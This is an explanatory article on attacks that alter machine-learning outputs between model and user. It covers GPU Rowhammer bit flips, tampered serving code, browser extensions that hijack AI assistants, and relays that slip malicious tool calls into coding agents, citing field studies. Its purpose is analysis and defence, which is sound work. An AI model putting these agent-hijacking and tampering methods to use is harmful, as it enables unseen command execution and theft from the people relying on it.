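# Attacks on the integrity of machine-learning outputs, and what masking and redaction can guarantee

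## What is output integrity, and what do masking and redaction do to it?

A machine-learning system has output integrity when the output a person or program acts on is the one the stated model produced, changed only in authorised and announced ways. An attacker can violate it by altering the output without changing the model. The usual example comes from the *Machine Learning Security Top 10* (OWASP, 2023), published by the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, a largely volunteer community that produces free security guidance. It describes a hospital that uses a model to diagnose diseases. An attacker gains access to the model's output and alters it, so patients receive incorrect diagnoses and then incorrect treatment, and some may die.

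The scenario belongs to entry ML09:2023, "Output Integrity Attack", in which an attacker "aims to modify or manipulate the output of a machine learning model", either to change its behaviour or to harm the system around it. The reference to behaviour is imprecise, because the hospital attacker doesn't need to touch the model. It would still return the same diagnosis for the same scan, and only the copy that reaches the doctor is different. OWASP lists the possible attackers as outsiders and insiders with access to the model's inputs and outputs, and third parties who handle both and tamper with them to get a result they want. It rates the attack as easy to carry out and moderately hard to detect, but warns that these ratings fit only this scenario. The ratings are judgements, not measurements, and OWASP still labels the list a draft.

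The entry lists six defences, none of them a form of masking or redaction: digital signatures and hashes on the results, an encrypted channel between the model and the display, checks of the results for unexpected values, tamper-evident logs of inputs and outputs, regular software updates, and monitoring with audits. They would help the hospital to very different degrees. A check for unexpected values catches a disease code that does not exist, but it misses an attacker who changes "malignant" to "benign", because "benign" is a normal finding in a scan report. Investigators can use logs to find the change later, perhaps after the treatment. An encrypted channel stops an attacker on the network but not one who has broken into the machine at either end. A signature can stop the altered report at the doctor's screen, provided that the software there checks the signature and fails closed, meaning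 that it refuses to act when it cannot complete the check.

### Three questions about one diagnosis

Let x be the input (the scan), M the model the hospital believes it is using, r the response the service produced, and r' the response delivered to the doctor. Computation integrity means that M computed r from x, delivery integrity means that r' equals r, and correctness means that r is right. Any one of the three can fail while the other two hold, as the first three cases in the table show.

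| What happens | Did M compute r from x? | Does r' equal r? | Is r right? |
|---|---|---|---|
| The service runs a cheaper model in place of M, and the cheaper model happens to read the scan correctly | No | Yes | Yes |
| M finds the tumour, and an attacker changes "malignant" to "benign" on the way to the doctor | Yes | No | Yes |
| M overlooks the tumour, and the doctor receives exactly what M produced | Yes | Yes | No |
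| Someone doctors the scan before the hospital submits it, and M misreads it | Yes | Yes | No |
| M learned from training data that an attacker had poisoned, and misreads the scan | Yes | Yes | No |
| An attacker alters M's parameters on the server, and the altered model misreads the scan | No | Yes | No |

The swapped model does no harm in this case. But the hospital trusts the diagnoses because of tests done on M, and those tests don't show how well a model unknown to the hospital performs. The overlooked tumour involves no attacker, and no integrity check will detect it.

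Definitions differ on this last point. A 2007 standard for industrial control systems, quoted in the IADC Lexicon's *Data Integrity* entry, limits the term to "constancy of and confidence in data values" and excludes the information that the values represent. The *Data Integrity* page of IEEE, an engineering association, also includes the correctness of stored values. The narrow sense is more useful for model outputs, because a hospital can use cryptography to verify that a report is unchanged but not that it is true.

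The OWASP list has separate entries for doctored scans and poisoned training data. An adversarial input (ML01) is one that an attacker has deliberately altered to mislead the model. OWASP gives the example of a cat picture with small, carefully chosen changes that a classifier mistakes for a dog. *Study medical AI diagnosis models can be manipulated to output wrong diagnosis*, from SC Media, reports that University of Pittsburgh researchers misled diagnostic models with falsified images. Data poisoning (ML02) happens earlier, when an attacker corrupts the examples from which the model learns, for instance by bribing the people who label them. In both cases the model itself produces the bad r, so signing that r, delivering it intact and proving that M computed it do not help the patient.

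The literature often files these attacks under "integrity" too, which can cause confusion. *Adversarial Machine Learning* (Vassilev, Oprea and colleagues, 2025) sets out the taxonomy of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST). According to the OECD's summary, the taxonomy sorts attackers' goals into violations of availability, integrity and privacy, and for predictive models it covers adversarial inputs (under the name "evasion"), poisoning and attacks on privacy. The OWASP AI Exchange, a larger sister project of the Top 10, describes evasion in *2. Threats through use* as damaging the integrity of model behaviour, which is different from the integrity of an output after the model has produced it.

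Whether an attack breaks computation integrity depends on when the parties fix x and M. If the attacker alters the scan before the hospital submits it, M still computes its answer from the x it was given, so computation integrity holds. If the attacker swaps the scan between the hospital and the model, M computes its answer from something other than x, and computation integrity fails. The same applies to the model. In an example from OWASP, an attacker changes the parameters of a bank's model for reading handwritten cheques so that it reads a "5" as a "2". If the bank has a fingerprint of the parameters it approved, it can detect the change. If the attacker poisoned the training data before the bank approved the model, the fingerprint matches even though the model misreads the cheques.

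### Hashes, signatures, TLS and enclaves

The fingerprint is a hash, a short value, commonly 256 bits long, that a public procedure computes from data of any length. The same data always give the same hash, changing one letter gives a completely different one, and with a sound procedure nobody can feasibly find two texts that share a hash. The hospital's server computes H(r) from the report r when the model finishes, and the doctor's software computes H(r') from the report r' that arrives. If the two values match, then for all practical purposes r' = r. But anyone can compute a hash, so an attacker who can rewrite the report can also replace a hash sent with it.

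A digital signature removes this weakness. The signer keeps a private key, publishes a matching public key, and computes a signature from the private key and the hash of r. Anyone with the public key can check the signature against the response, but nobody can produce a valid signature without the private key. The signature can reveal only changes made after signing, and NIST's *Integrity authentication* entry likewise covers modification only from the time the signature was created. If someone alters the diagnosis before the server signs it, the doctor receives a false report with a valid signature.

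TLS (Transport Layer Security) encrypts traffic on a single connection between two machines and lets the receiving machine detect changes made on the way. Many users, however, reach a model through a relay, a service that decrypts, reads and forwards the traffic. The relay has a separate TLS connection on each side, so whoever runs it can change r without breaking either connection. Security engineers call an attacker in this position a man-in-the-middle. OWASP AI Exchange's *4. Runtime conventional security threats* treats this as an ordinary information security problem for which standard controls exist.

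Hashes, signatures and TLS deal with what happens to r after it is produced. It is harder to establish that M computed r, because the hospital usually cannot see the provider's machines. An attested enclave can help. It is an isolated part of a processor that can prove to a remote party which code it runs, and it is designed to keep the rest of the machine, including its administrator, from reading or altering what is inside. On request, the chip signs a hash of the code it has loaded, and the hospital compares this with the hash of the code it expects. If the comparison also covers the model's parameters, and the enclave signs its responses, the hospital has good evidence that M produced r. The OWASP AI Exchange recommends such an environment for a more modest purpose, which is to help protect the model's integrity.

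### Tokens, tool calls and the forms of masking

A language model generates text in tokens, which are words or pieces of words. At each step, the model assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software around it picks one and adds it to the text before the next step.

A tool call is the structured part of a response that tells an agent's software which action to run. OWASP AI Exchange's *2. Input threats* advises operators to log, among other things, the tool name, arguments and target of each call. A hospital agent's tool might be a function that orders drugs, with the patient and the dose as its arguments. Someone who changes 5 mg to 50 mg in the call changes the order. A doctor might notice the same error in a written report, but the agent's software may run the call before anyone reads it.

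Masking means any deliberate hiding or blocking of part of an output, before or after the model generates it. It takes several forms.

- Score masking withholds, rounds or perturbs the probabilities that accompany a prediction. The hospital's model might report "malignant" and leave out the 0.93 that came with it. This costs the user something, and the UK's National Cyber Security Centre makes the trade-off between security and the output a model gives its users one of its principles, in NCSC's *Principles for the security of machine learning*.
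- Token masking sets the probability of forbidden next tokens to zero while the model is writing. A hospital could use it to confine a drug-ordering agent to the names of drugs that the pharmacy stocks.
- Redaction removes or replaces parts of a finished output, such as the patient's name in a report.
- Redaction of signed records does the same to an output that already carries a signature. Under an ordinary signature scheme the removal of a single character makes the check fail. Cryptographers have designed redactable signatures, which still verify after permitted removals.

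Token masking stands somewhat apart from the rest. It acts before r exists, so there is no unmasked response with which to compare the result. The mask is part of the computation, and "the stated model" has to mean M together with its mask. A provider that adds a mask without saying so has in effect supplied a different model. (The OWASP AI Exchange also uses "masking" for random delays or noise that hide a model's response times from eavesdroppers, a separate technique that happens to share the name.)

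### Integrity after redaction

Redaction poses a problem for any definition of integrity because it changes the output. A hospital might remove the patient's name from a report before sending it to a research registry, while an attacker might remove the word "no" from "no sign of malignancy". Both changes fail the test r' = r, and in both cases the hash no longer matches.

Standard definitions of data integrity allow authorised changes. NIST's *data integrity* entry requires that data have not been altered "in an unauthorized manner" in storage, during processing or in transit. NIST records the same qualifier in the Security Rule under HIPAA, the US health-privacy law. IEEE's definition requires values to stay the same unless someone makes a deliberate, authorised modification.

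For a redacted output, integrity has to mean that r' = m(r), where m is an announced rule that an authorised party has applied. The rule might be "replace every patient name with the word PATIENT". If m changes nothing, the definition reduces to r' = r.

The announcement matters because a reader who does not know the rule cannot tell a report that never mentioned allergies from one whose paragraph on allergies was removed. Authorisation matters because a relay operator who strips names unasked may produce the same text as the hospital's privacy office, but nobody agreed to let that operator edit medical reports or will know what else the operator changes later. The equality matters because it excludes all changes other than those the rule requires.

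How much protection this gives depends on how narrow m is. If m allows any word to be deleted, the redactor can delete "no" and reverse the meaning of a sentence. The redactor can also often choose among several rules. If a hospital may remove any of a report's ten fields, there are 2^10 = 1,024 permitted rules, counting the one that removes nothing, and a recipient who verifies the result learns only that r' came from r by one of them. All of the resulting versions have integrity in the sense just defined, but some may mislead badly, such as one that keeps the diagnosis and drops the field giving its uncertainty.

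In practice, the recipient of a redacted report also cannot compute m(r) and compare it with what they received, because redaction withholds part of r. They must either trust the redactor or rely on cryptographic evidence in place of the missing text.

Redaction exists mainly for confidentiality and was not designed to do any of this, and current guidance still treats it as a confidentiality control. *AI Security Guide and Risk Assessment Tool* (Hodgson, Schwindt and colleagues, 2026), from the RAND Corporation, matches security controls to the threats in OWASP's lists. It matches the detection and redaction of sensitive information to disclosure, model inversion (the extraction of private information from a model) and membership inference (finding out whether a given person's record was in the training data), but not to output integrity (ML09). That control covers data "before processing",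 but the guide also includes a check of outputs for leaked information, which it matches to the same privacy threats and again not to ML09. OWASP likewise recommends score masking, in the form of random noise on a model's predictions, under membership inference but not under output integrity.

RAND's controls against ML09 include encryption in transit, tamper-evident logs, monitoring, and validating output formats with deterministic code. The control closest to masking is a filter that searches text for sensitive content and handles what it finds. This filter may keep a harmful response from reaching a user, but a response that passes it could have come from any model, or from an attacker who knew what the filter searches for.

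## Where can an output be changed between the model and its user?

A response passes through the processor that runs the model, the software around the model, the network, the reader's browser and often a database. Someone can change it at any of these points. The access they need ranges from an administrator's password to a browser extension, and the evidence they leave also varies widely.

### Bit flips in the processor's memory

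Most large models run on graphics processing units (GPUs). While a model runs, the GPU's memory holds the model's parameters, or weights, and stores each bit as an electric charge in a tiny cell. The cells are arranged in rows. If a program reads one row many thousands of times in quick succession, charge leaks from the cells in nearby rows, and a bit there may flip from 0 to 1 or from 1 to 0. An attacker can use this effect, which security researchers call Rowhammer, to change other people's data in memory by rapidly and repeatedly reading their own.

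In *GPUHammer*, Lin, Qu and Saileshwar (2025) carried out the first such attack on a discrete graphics card, the 48 GB NVIDIA RTX A6000, a popular workstation card that cloud providers also rent out. Its memory appears to have a defence that tracks heavily used rows and refreshes their neighbours before they lose too much charge. But the defence can track only 16 rows in each bank (a section of the memory), so the attackers read 17 or more in rotation. They spent about 30 hours on each of four banks and flipped eight bits in total. They flipped none on an A100, a server GPU with a different type of memory, or on an RTX 3080 laptop GPU.

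Flipping one bit in the right place can ruin a model. The weights in this experiment were 16-bit numbers of the form ±1.f × 2^(e − 15), where f is the fraction and e the exponent. Changing the top bit of e from 0 to 1 adds 16 to the exponent, which multiplies the weight by 2^16 = 65,536. A weight of 0.05 becomes about 3,277, and the error spreads through the rest of the calculation. Such a flip reduced the accuracy of the image classifier ResNet50 from 80.26% to 0.08% on ImageNet, a 1,000-category test where random guessing would score 0.1%. Across five classifiers, average accuracy fell from 71.26% to 0.08%. These are the worst results from 50 attempts per model, which took about half an hour, although eight attempts were usually enough. Flips in the fraction f changed accuracy by less than 0.1 percentage points.

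The attacker needs permission to run programs on the same GPU as the victim, which is possible when a cloud provider lets customers take turns on one card. The attacker also has to get the victim's weights into a vulnerable part of the GPU's memory. Lin and colleagues did this by reserving a large block of memory, finding a weak cell in it, and releasing the piece containing that cell just before the victim's program asked for memory. NVIDIA's confidential-computing mode gives each customer whole GPUs, which blocks this route of attack.

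A hospital would soon notice a model that is wrong 99.9% of the time, so this attack is better suited to sabotage than to changing one patient's diagnosis. In *GPUBreach*, Lin, Yan and colleagues (2026) gained much finer control of the same card by flipping bits in its page tables, which record where each program's data lie. They could then read and write any program's GPU memory. By changing a single branch in the code of NVIDIA's cuBLAS mathematics library, they cut the accuracy of models from as much as 80% to 0%. The weights stayed correct, so a hospital that checked their hash against an approved one would find nothing wrong. This demonstration still destroyed the models' accuracy completely, but an attacker who can write anywhere in the memory could presumably also alter chosen results.

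Both experiments assumed the card's error-correcting code (ECC) was off. ECC stores extra bits with the data so the memory can repair a single flipped bit. NVIDIA recommends it as the main defence against Rowhammer, but it slowed machine-learning programs on the A6000 by 3–10% in the 2025 tests, and *GPUBreach* found two cloud providers that left it off by default.

That advice now looks inadequate. In *GPUThor*, Lin, Qu and colleagues (2026) read the rows next to the target much more often than the decoy rows used to divert the memory's defence. With ECC off, the attack produced 114,488 flips per gigabyte on the A6000, compared with 16 in the 2025 work, and between 72,768 and 377,552 across four NVIDIA cards. At these rates, several flips can land in the same small block of data. ECC can detect two flips in a block but cannot repair them, and it may miss three or "correct" them to a wrong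 value. With ECC on, the attack crashed an A6000 about once an hour. The researchers also gained unauthorised privileges, partly because programs keep using the corrupted data for about 10 milliseconds between the detection of a double flip and the shutdown.

With ECC on, the card counts the errors it corrects, so an administrator can watch for a sudden rise as a sign of the attack. However, the counter becomes unreliable after a few thousand errors, and the separate record of failed rows misses silent corruptions.

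### The serving software

Ordinary software between the GPU and the network inserts the user's text into a prompt template with the operator's instructions, picks each token according to sampling settings, and prepares the finished text for delivery. OWASP's *Runtime conventional security threats* warns that an attacker who compromises this input or output logic can change a model's behaviour, which does not require changing the weights.

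The simplest change to the hospital's system would be one line in the output-handling code that replaces "malignant" with "benign". An attacker could make it apply to a single patient. An attacker could also change the prompt template before the model runs, for instance by adding an instruction to describe doubtful findings as harmless. The model would then work correctly, but on a prompt that the hospital did not intend.

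Changes to sampling settings are harder to spot. The temperature T, a common setting, controls how often the software picks less likely tokens. The software replaces each probability p with p^(1/T) and rescales the results to add up to 1. Suppose the model gives "malignant" a probability of 0.93 and "benign" 0.07. At T = 1, the software writes "benign" in 7% of runs. If someone raises T to 2, the square roots of the two numbers are about 0.964 and 0.265, and after rescaling "benign" has a probability of about 0.22. The error rate has roughly tripled. Nobody could detect the change from one report, because the original settings would sometimes have produced the same words.

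These edits require the ability to deploy code or change settings on the server. Administrators and some developers have it, and so does an intruder who steals their credentials. If the attacker uses the normal release process, the version history and deployment logs record the change. An intruder who edits a running server directly avoids that record and may be able to delete the server's own logs, so it helps to keep a copy elsewhere. The operator can also compare hashes of the running code with those of the approved version, but this detects a changed template or temperature only if the hashes cover the settings too.

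### Three bugs and no attacker

In August and September 2025, Anthropic's servers gave some users of its Claude models worse responses, though nobody had attacked the servers. Anthropic's *A postmortem of three recent issues* attributes this to three overlapping bugs.

The first appeared on 5 August, when the system began sending about 0.8% of requests for the model Sonnet 4 to servers configured for a forthcoming version with a much longer context window (the amount of text a model can take in at once). On 29 August, a routine change in how Anthropic spread traffic between servers increased the share of misrouted requests, which peaked at 16% during one hour on 31 August. About 30% of the users of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming tool, had at least one message misrouted. Some had many, because follow-up messages tended to go to the same server as the first.

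The second bug came from a faulty configuration that Anthropic installed on 25 August on servers with TPUs, Google's AI processors. It sometimes gave a high probability to tokens that should almost never appear, so some answers to English questions contained Thai or Chinese characters, and some code contained obvious syntax errors.

At almost the same time, Anthropic deployed new code for choosing tokens, which exposed a hidden fault in the compiler, the program that translates code into instructions for the TPUs. To save time, the software used an approximate search for the most probable tokens, but for some batch sizes the search returned completely wrong results and could drop the most probable token. In the hospital example, that would remove "malignant" and leave "benign". The same prompt could work on one request and fail on the next, and the fault appeared or disappeared depending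 on whether debugging tools were on. Anthropic confirmed the fault in Haiku 3.5 and suspected it in two other models. It did not report what share of requests the second or third bug affected.

Users began to complain in early August, but Anthropic did not open its investigation until late August, about three weeks after the first bug appeared. It deployed a fix for the misrouting on 4 September, 30 days after the bug began. Anthropic's public incident log, *Model output quality* (2025), records that the company had identified the causes by 12 September and closed the incident on 17 September.

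The company's tests contributed to the delay by missing the problem, partly because Claude often recovers from isolated mistakes. Privacy rules protected users by limiting which conversations engineers could read, but this also made it harder to find the bad responses needed to reproduce the bugs. Anthropic has since promised to run more sensitive tests continuously on its live systems.

Delivery integrity held throughout, because users received what the servers had produced. If Anthropic had signed each response, the signatures would have been valid. An attested enclave would not necessarily have caught the second and third bugs either, since Anthropic had itself chosen to deploy the faulty configuration and code. Computation integrity is less clear. The weights were the right ones, but if "the stated model" includes the way it is meant to choose tokens, some users did not get that model.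 (A provider may also substitute a cheaper model on purpose, which is a separate problem.)

### The browser

Except at a relay, TLS protects the response on the network until the browser decrypts it. The browser then builds the page as a structure called the Document Object Model (DOM), which holds the text box, the buttons and the chatbot's answer. A browser extension with permission to run scripts on the page can read and write to the DOM, so it can change the question before it reaches the model, or the answer before it reaches the user.

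**Changes to the prompt.** In July 2025, the browser-security company LayerX published an attack called Man-in-the-Prompt. LayerX's *A New Vector for Prompt Injection Attacks* describes an extension with no special permissions that opened ChatGPT in a background tab, submitted a prompt, sent the answer to an outside server and deleted the conversation from the user's history. A second demonstration used Google's Gemini assistant to find and extract a user's emails and documents, even when the user had closed the assistant's panel. The attack did not need to alter an output, because the model was answering prompts that the user had not written.

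The Hacker News' *One Extension Could Hijack AI Assistants* (2026) reports a more powerful attack called BragJack, from the company Forever Security, on assistants that can act inside the browser. The model runs on the vendor's servers and chooses actions, which a component in the browser carries out. That component accepts commands from only one trusted web page, such as perplexity.ai for Perplexity's browser, Comet. An extension cannot command the component directly. But with two common permissions, one to change web pages and one to change network traffic, the researchers' extension inserted its own code into the trusted page, and the component carried out that code's commands as if they came from the vendor.

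The attack worked on five products: Gemini Live in Chrome, Comet, Microsoft Edge, Opera Neon and Anthropic's Claude in Chrome. The extension could control the agent on all of them except Gemini Live. It could open local files through Chrome and Comet, and could also turn on the camera and microphone through Chrome. Google fixed the flaw in January 2026 and Microsoft in July. The findings on the other three products rest on Forever Security's own account, though it received bounties for them. All of these were demonstrations, not attacks seen in the wild.

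BragJack changes the agent's instructions, and none of the abilities the researchers list involves rewriting the answer on the screen. *Security Check-in Quick Hits* (Trent, 2026) calls the technique "Prompt Forcing", in which the extension supplies the agent's complete instructions instead of inserting a few words into a page the agent reads. For the user, the effect may be much like that of a forged tool call, because the browser takes an action that neither the user nor the model working on their request chose.

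LayerX found a related flaw in Claude's Chrome extension. According to SecurityWeek's *Vulnerability in Claude Extension for Chrome Exposes AI Agent to Takeover*, the extension accepted commands from any other extension's scripts because it did not check who owned the scripts. IANS's *Flaw in Claude’s Chrome Extension Allows Threat Actors to Hijack AI Agents* (2026) reports that attackers could also manipulate the assistant's interface and erase the evidence.

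**Changes to the displayed answer.** In October 2025 the security company SquareX showed how an extension can draw an exact copy of a browser's AI sidebar. According to SecurityWeek, the fake sidebar sends the user's question to a language model connected by the attacker, and most of the answers are ordinary. When the user asks for instructions, the extension adds harmful steps. These may include altered links or system commands, according to SiliconANGLE (2025). SquareX demonstrated the attack on Comet, and its *AI Sidebar Spoofing* says the attack is also possible on Brave, Edge and Firefox. Delivery and computation integrity both fail because the question never reaches the assistant the user believes they are consulting.

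*Beware EviLLM* (2026) describes a browser extension for planting security vulnerabilities through ChatGPT. It needs access to the clipboard, a script on the ChatGPT page and a connection to the attacker's server. Programmers often copy code out of a chat, so an extension that can write to the clipboard could change the code they paste while the answer on the page stays correct.

Malicious browser extensions are common, but the documented ones mostly steal data. *Malicious GenAI Chrome Extensions* (2025) examined 29 that posed as AI tools and found that they mainly took information or redirected users to other sites. Security Boulevard's *Widely Used Malicious Extensions Steal ChatGPT, DeepSeek Conversations* (2025) reports that one extension with more than 6 million users collected every prompt and response from ten popular AI systems. An extension that reads answers from the page could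 usually rewrite them too. A legitimate extension can also become malicious after a user installs it. The same report describes a group that built up trust in legitimate extensions over seven years and then added malicious code in updates.

An extension that rewrites an answer leaves little evidence at the provider, whose logs show a normal response. If the extension changed only the display, the user could find the original by opening the same conversation on another device. An injected prompt, by contrast, appears in the chat history unless the extension deletes it, as LayerX's did.

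### Stored outputs

Many outputs are used long after the model produced them. A bank may save a credit score, and a hospital may copy a model's finding into a patient's record. Anyone who can write to the database can change the saved copy, whether they are an employee, an intruder or a program with more permissions than it needs. The model and its server are no longer involved, so the change will not appear in their logs.

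An attacker can sometimes change stored outputs without direct access to the database. OWASP gives the example of a customer-support system in which several AI agents share a memory. An attacker sends a request that mentions an invented return policy, and one agent saves a summary of it. The other agents then take that summary as input and repeat the policy to customers until someone removes the entry.

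Medical records are a difficult case because people have good reasons to change them. A radiologist who disagrees with a model may correct its finding, and the record then no longer matches the hash of the original output. An attack would cause the same mismatch, so investigators also need the original text and a record of who changed it and when. For an agent's memory, OWASP recommends recording the source, writer and time of each entry in logs that nobody can rewrite. The same approach would suit a hospital, though OWASP concedes that telling legitimate updates from malicious ones remains difficult at scale.

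OWASP's hospital scenario is hypothetical, and the University of Pittsburgh researchers changed the images given to diagnostic models rather than the results. But the scenario requires no new technique, since an intruder with write access to the results could change them with an ordinary database command.

TLS would prevent very few of the changes described here, because most of them happen before the server encrypts the response or after the recipient decrypts it.

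| Position | Access the attacker needs | Would TLS help? |
|---|---|---|
| GPU memory | Permission to run programs on the same GPU, and vulnerable memory | No, the error occurs before encryption |
| Serving software | Ability to deploy code or change settings (a bug needs no attacker) | No, TLS would protect the altered response |
| Network connection | Control of a point between the two machines | Yes |
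| Relay | Control of the relay, as its operator or an intruder | No, the relay decrypts the traffic |
| Browser | An installed extension that can run scripts on the page | No, the browser has already decrypted the response |
| Database or chat history | Write access, or a way to get false text saved | Only while the data travel to and from storage |

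## What can a relay change, and who notices?

A relay can change anything in the traffic it forwards, because its users give it the plaintext. A developer uses a relay by entering its address in the software in place of the provider's. The user's TLS connection then ends at the relay, which attaches the key of one of its provider accounts and forwards the request over a second connection. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) points out that the prompt, the response and every tool's inputs and outputs are therefore readable inside the relay during each request. An attacker on the network would have to break the encryption or forge a certificate to get the access that users give the relay's operator.

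Developers use relays because a relay offers many providers' models through one account, can switch to another provider when one fails, and often charges less than the providers do. A relay may also be the only way to reach providers that restrict access by region. In *Rewriting the Response Path*, Luo, Zhang and colleagues (2026) examined the 60 most-used applications on OpenRouter, a large commercial relay. A custom model address made sense for 25 of them, and 23 of those let users supply their own key or address.

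Relays also buy access from one another. *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* (2026), a blog post about a field study of 428 relays, gives the example of a developer who buys from a reseller, which buys from a larger supplier, which reaches the model's provider through OpenRouter. The developer chose only the reseller and cannot see the rest of the chain. If one relay alters a response, any honest relays between it and the developer unknowingly pass on the altered version.

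### The text and the tool call

An agent's response can be written as r = (t, a), where t is the text a person reads and a is the list of tool calls the software executes. The software runs the calls in a without checking that t describes them.

A relay can raise the hospital agent's drug order from 5 mg to 50 mg and leave the agent's sentence "I am ordering 5 mg" unchanged, so the doctor reads 5 mg while the pharmacy receives an order for 50 mg. The altered call names the same tool, has the same fields and contains a valid number, so a format check will accept it.

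A doctor who opened the tool call would see the mismatch, but an attacker can make it harder to spot. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (Fu, Li and colleagues, 2026) tests four versions of the attack. In the crudest, the relay discards the model's response and delivers a malicious tool call with no text. In the second, it keeps the whole response and adds one action, so that (t, a) becomes (t, a + b), where b is the attacker's tool call. The model's original actions still run, and t remains a true but incomplete account of what happens. The third version also rewrites t to give b a plausible reason. In the fourth, a model writes the entire response from scratch with b included, so nothing marks where b was added.

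The provider logs the response it sent, r, and the user logs the one that arrived, r', so only a relay handles both. The user could check a provider's signature on the tool calls, or the attestation of a relay that runs in an enclave, but the field study found no major provider that signed its tool calls.

### What 428 relays did

Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026) published that field study, *Your Agent Is Mine*, in April. They bought access to 28 relays from sellers on Taobao, Xianyu and Shopify-hosted shops, and collected 400 free relays from public online communities. They opened an account with each relay and ran a coding agent through it on tasks that lead to shell commands, package installations and file changes. The agent worked in a sandbox, an isolated environment where it could safely execute every tool call the relay returned. The sandbox recorded network connections, file changes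 and new processes, and a second AI agent reviewed the suspicious cases.

The researchers also planted credentials in the traffic. Some were Amazon Web Services (AWS) canary keys, whose only purpose was to reveal anyone who used them. Another was the private key to an Ethereum wallet holding a small amount of money.

| Behaviour | Paid relays (28) | Free relays (400) |
|---|---|---|
| Injected malicious code into tool calls | 1 | 8 |
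| Did so only under chosen conditions | 0 | 2 |
| Passed on an AWS key that someone later used | 0 | 17 |
| Passed on a wallet key that someone used to empty the wallet | 0 | 1 |

Liu and colleagues counted a relay as injecting only if it had changed a tool call to run a command or install a software package that an attacker controlled. A relay that quietly made the code worse would not have counted.

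A relay can replace the name of a package in an install command with a very similar name that the attacker has registered. This is harder to detect than a command that downloads a program from an unknown site, because the altered command still uses the normal public registry. The malicious package also stays on the machine after the user stops using the relay.

The use of planted credentials changed no output, so it did not violate output integrity. It also does not prove that the tested relay's operator stole them. *The Cost of Proxies* (2026), another blog post on the study, notes that the key may have leaked from a different relay further along the chain. The same uncertainty applies to the emptied wallet, which had held less than $50.

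### Tampering that waits for a condition

One of the two relays with triggers injected code only after passing on 50 requests without tampering. The other acted only when the agent was running commands without asking the user and the project was written in Rust or Go.

Conditions like these defeat spot checks. If a relay altered a random share p of responses, n test requests would catch it with probability 1 − (1 − p)^n. For p = 1%, 50 requests would catch it 39% of the time and 300 would catch it 95% of the time, so a tester could be more confident by sending more requests. More requests don't help if none of them meets the relay's trigger condition. A ten-request check will never expose a relay that waits for 50 requests, and repeating the check from new accounts won't help if the count restarts with each account. Similarly, ten thousand requests about a Python project would not expose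 the second relay.

The condition also selects victims who are less likely to notice the attack, because nobody is there to question a strange command when an agent runs unattended. Liu and colleagues found no injection by the other 419 relays but acknowledge some may have had triggers their tests did not set off.

In a more recent test, reported in *What the Middleman Delivers*, Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) sent harmless requests for code and installation instructions to 20 relays selling GPT-6 Astra or Claude Opus 5. They ran two rounds, 11 to 18 days apart, and confirmed no injections in 3,332 responses. If the responses were independent samples, the true injection rate would be below 0.09% with 95% confidence. But each request stood alone, with no secrets in it and no agent executing the results, so the test would have missed a relay that tampers only with unattended coding sessions.

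Four of the 20 relays returned tool calls when the request had explicitly disabled them. They returned 30 such calls in the first round, 24 of them from one relay, and none in the second. The calls named a dummy tool that does nothing, and Wu and colleagues did not run them. The providers' own interfaces returned no tool calls for the same requests. The researchers could not determine whether the relays had added the calls or a service further upstream had ignored the setting. Either way, an agent's software can catch and refuse any call that the request did not allow.

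Wu and colleagues also found signs that relays may change the request. For identical questions, five relays reported between about 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens than the official interface did. On one question, the official count was 36, while three relays reported more than 4,400. Either hidden instructions added to every request or false accounting could explain the difference. If the relays did add instructions, computation integrity failed before the model produced a response.

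### How common is it?

Nine relays out of 428 is 2.1%, but this is not an estimate for relays in general. Liu and colleagues sampled anonymous sellers and free public services, mostly Chinese-language ones, and left out company-run and invitation-only relays. *The Cost of Proxies* describes this as a convenience sample from the part of the market most likely to cause trouble. The paid group is also very small, with one injecting relay out of 28. Even if those 28 had been a random sample, that result would be compatible with a true rate anywhere from 0.1% to 18%.

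The market is far larger than Liu's sample. *80,000 relay servers help users in China* (Markovic, 2026) reports that the security company Team Cymru confirmed 10,867 relays in eight days of scanning data and later raised the count to more than 80,000. Liu's sample would be about 0.5% of that number. Most of the relays in Team Cymru's first count ran sub2api, one of two open-source programs that also dominated Liu's free group, so the two populations probably overlap. But Team Cymru could not read the traffic, and its count contains no information about tampering.

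Liu's count of nine and Wu's count of zero also can't be combined. Wu and colleagues required an English interface and payment by card or PayPal, which excludes many of the sellers Liu's team bought from, and the two groups sent different kinds of requests.

A count of dishonest relays may also understate how many people are at risk, because an honest relay can forward traffic to a bad one. Liu and colleagues set up decoy relays with weak security on 20 domains and 20 internet addresses, and other relays began routing their customers' traffic through them. The decoys handled about 2 billion tokens, including 440 sessions of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, on 398 projects or machines. An injected command could have reached the shell in all 440 sessions, and in 401 of them (91%) the agent was running commands without asking for approval. These users had chosen other relays and could not see where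 those relays sent their traffic.

Attackers can also take over an honest relay. In March 2026, someone published versions of LiteLLM, a widely used open-source relay program, with malicious code that collected credentials and cryptocurrency wallets. Help Net Security's *Command integrity breaks in the LLM routing layer* reports that this code had access to every request and response on the affected systems. It could therefore have rewritten tool calls, although the documented harm was theft.

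### Four coding agents and 400 malicious actions

A malicious tool call does no harm if the agent refuses to run it. Liu and colleagues built their own relay and showed that altered calls reached four agent programs in a valid format at least 99.6% of the time. They did not measure how many a permission prompt or sandbox would have stopped.

Fu and colleagues measured this with a test system called SIDEL, which records an ordinary session between a coding agent and a model. It then replays the model's responses to the agent with one altered, so that differences in the agent's behavior come from the alteration rather than the model's randomness.

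The researchers wrote 400 malicious tool calls by hand, 100 for each of four aims: running malicious code, adding bugs, stealing private data and compromising the software that a project depends on. They tried each call on three bug-fixing tasks from SWE-bench Lite, a collection of real problems reported by users of open-source software, for a total of 1,200 runs per configuration. Each run had one injection at a randomly chosen point.

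Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and OpenCode blocked no injections in any of the four versions of the attack when they had permission to act without asking. Fu and colleagues then compared ten built-in permission settings, some of them more restrictive, and the agents still blocked nothing. Claude Code's "plan" setting, for example, is meant to let the agent read files but not change them. But it works by instructing the model, so it did not stop a malicious call that came from outside the model.

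These results apply to agents working unattended. Fu and colleagues left out the Claude Code setting that asks a person to approve actions, because they wanted to measure the software rather than the user. They also ran each combination of task and injection only once, and their handwritten attacks may differ from those of real criminals. But a result of zero out of 1,200 in every configuration is unlikely to be due to chance. The agents had no way to check where a tool call came from.

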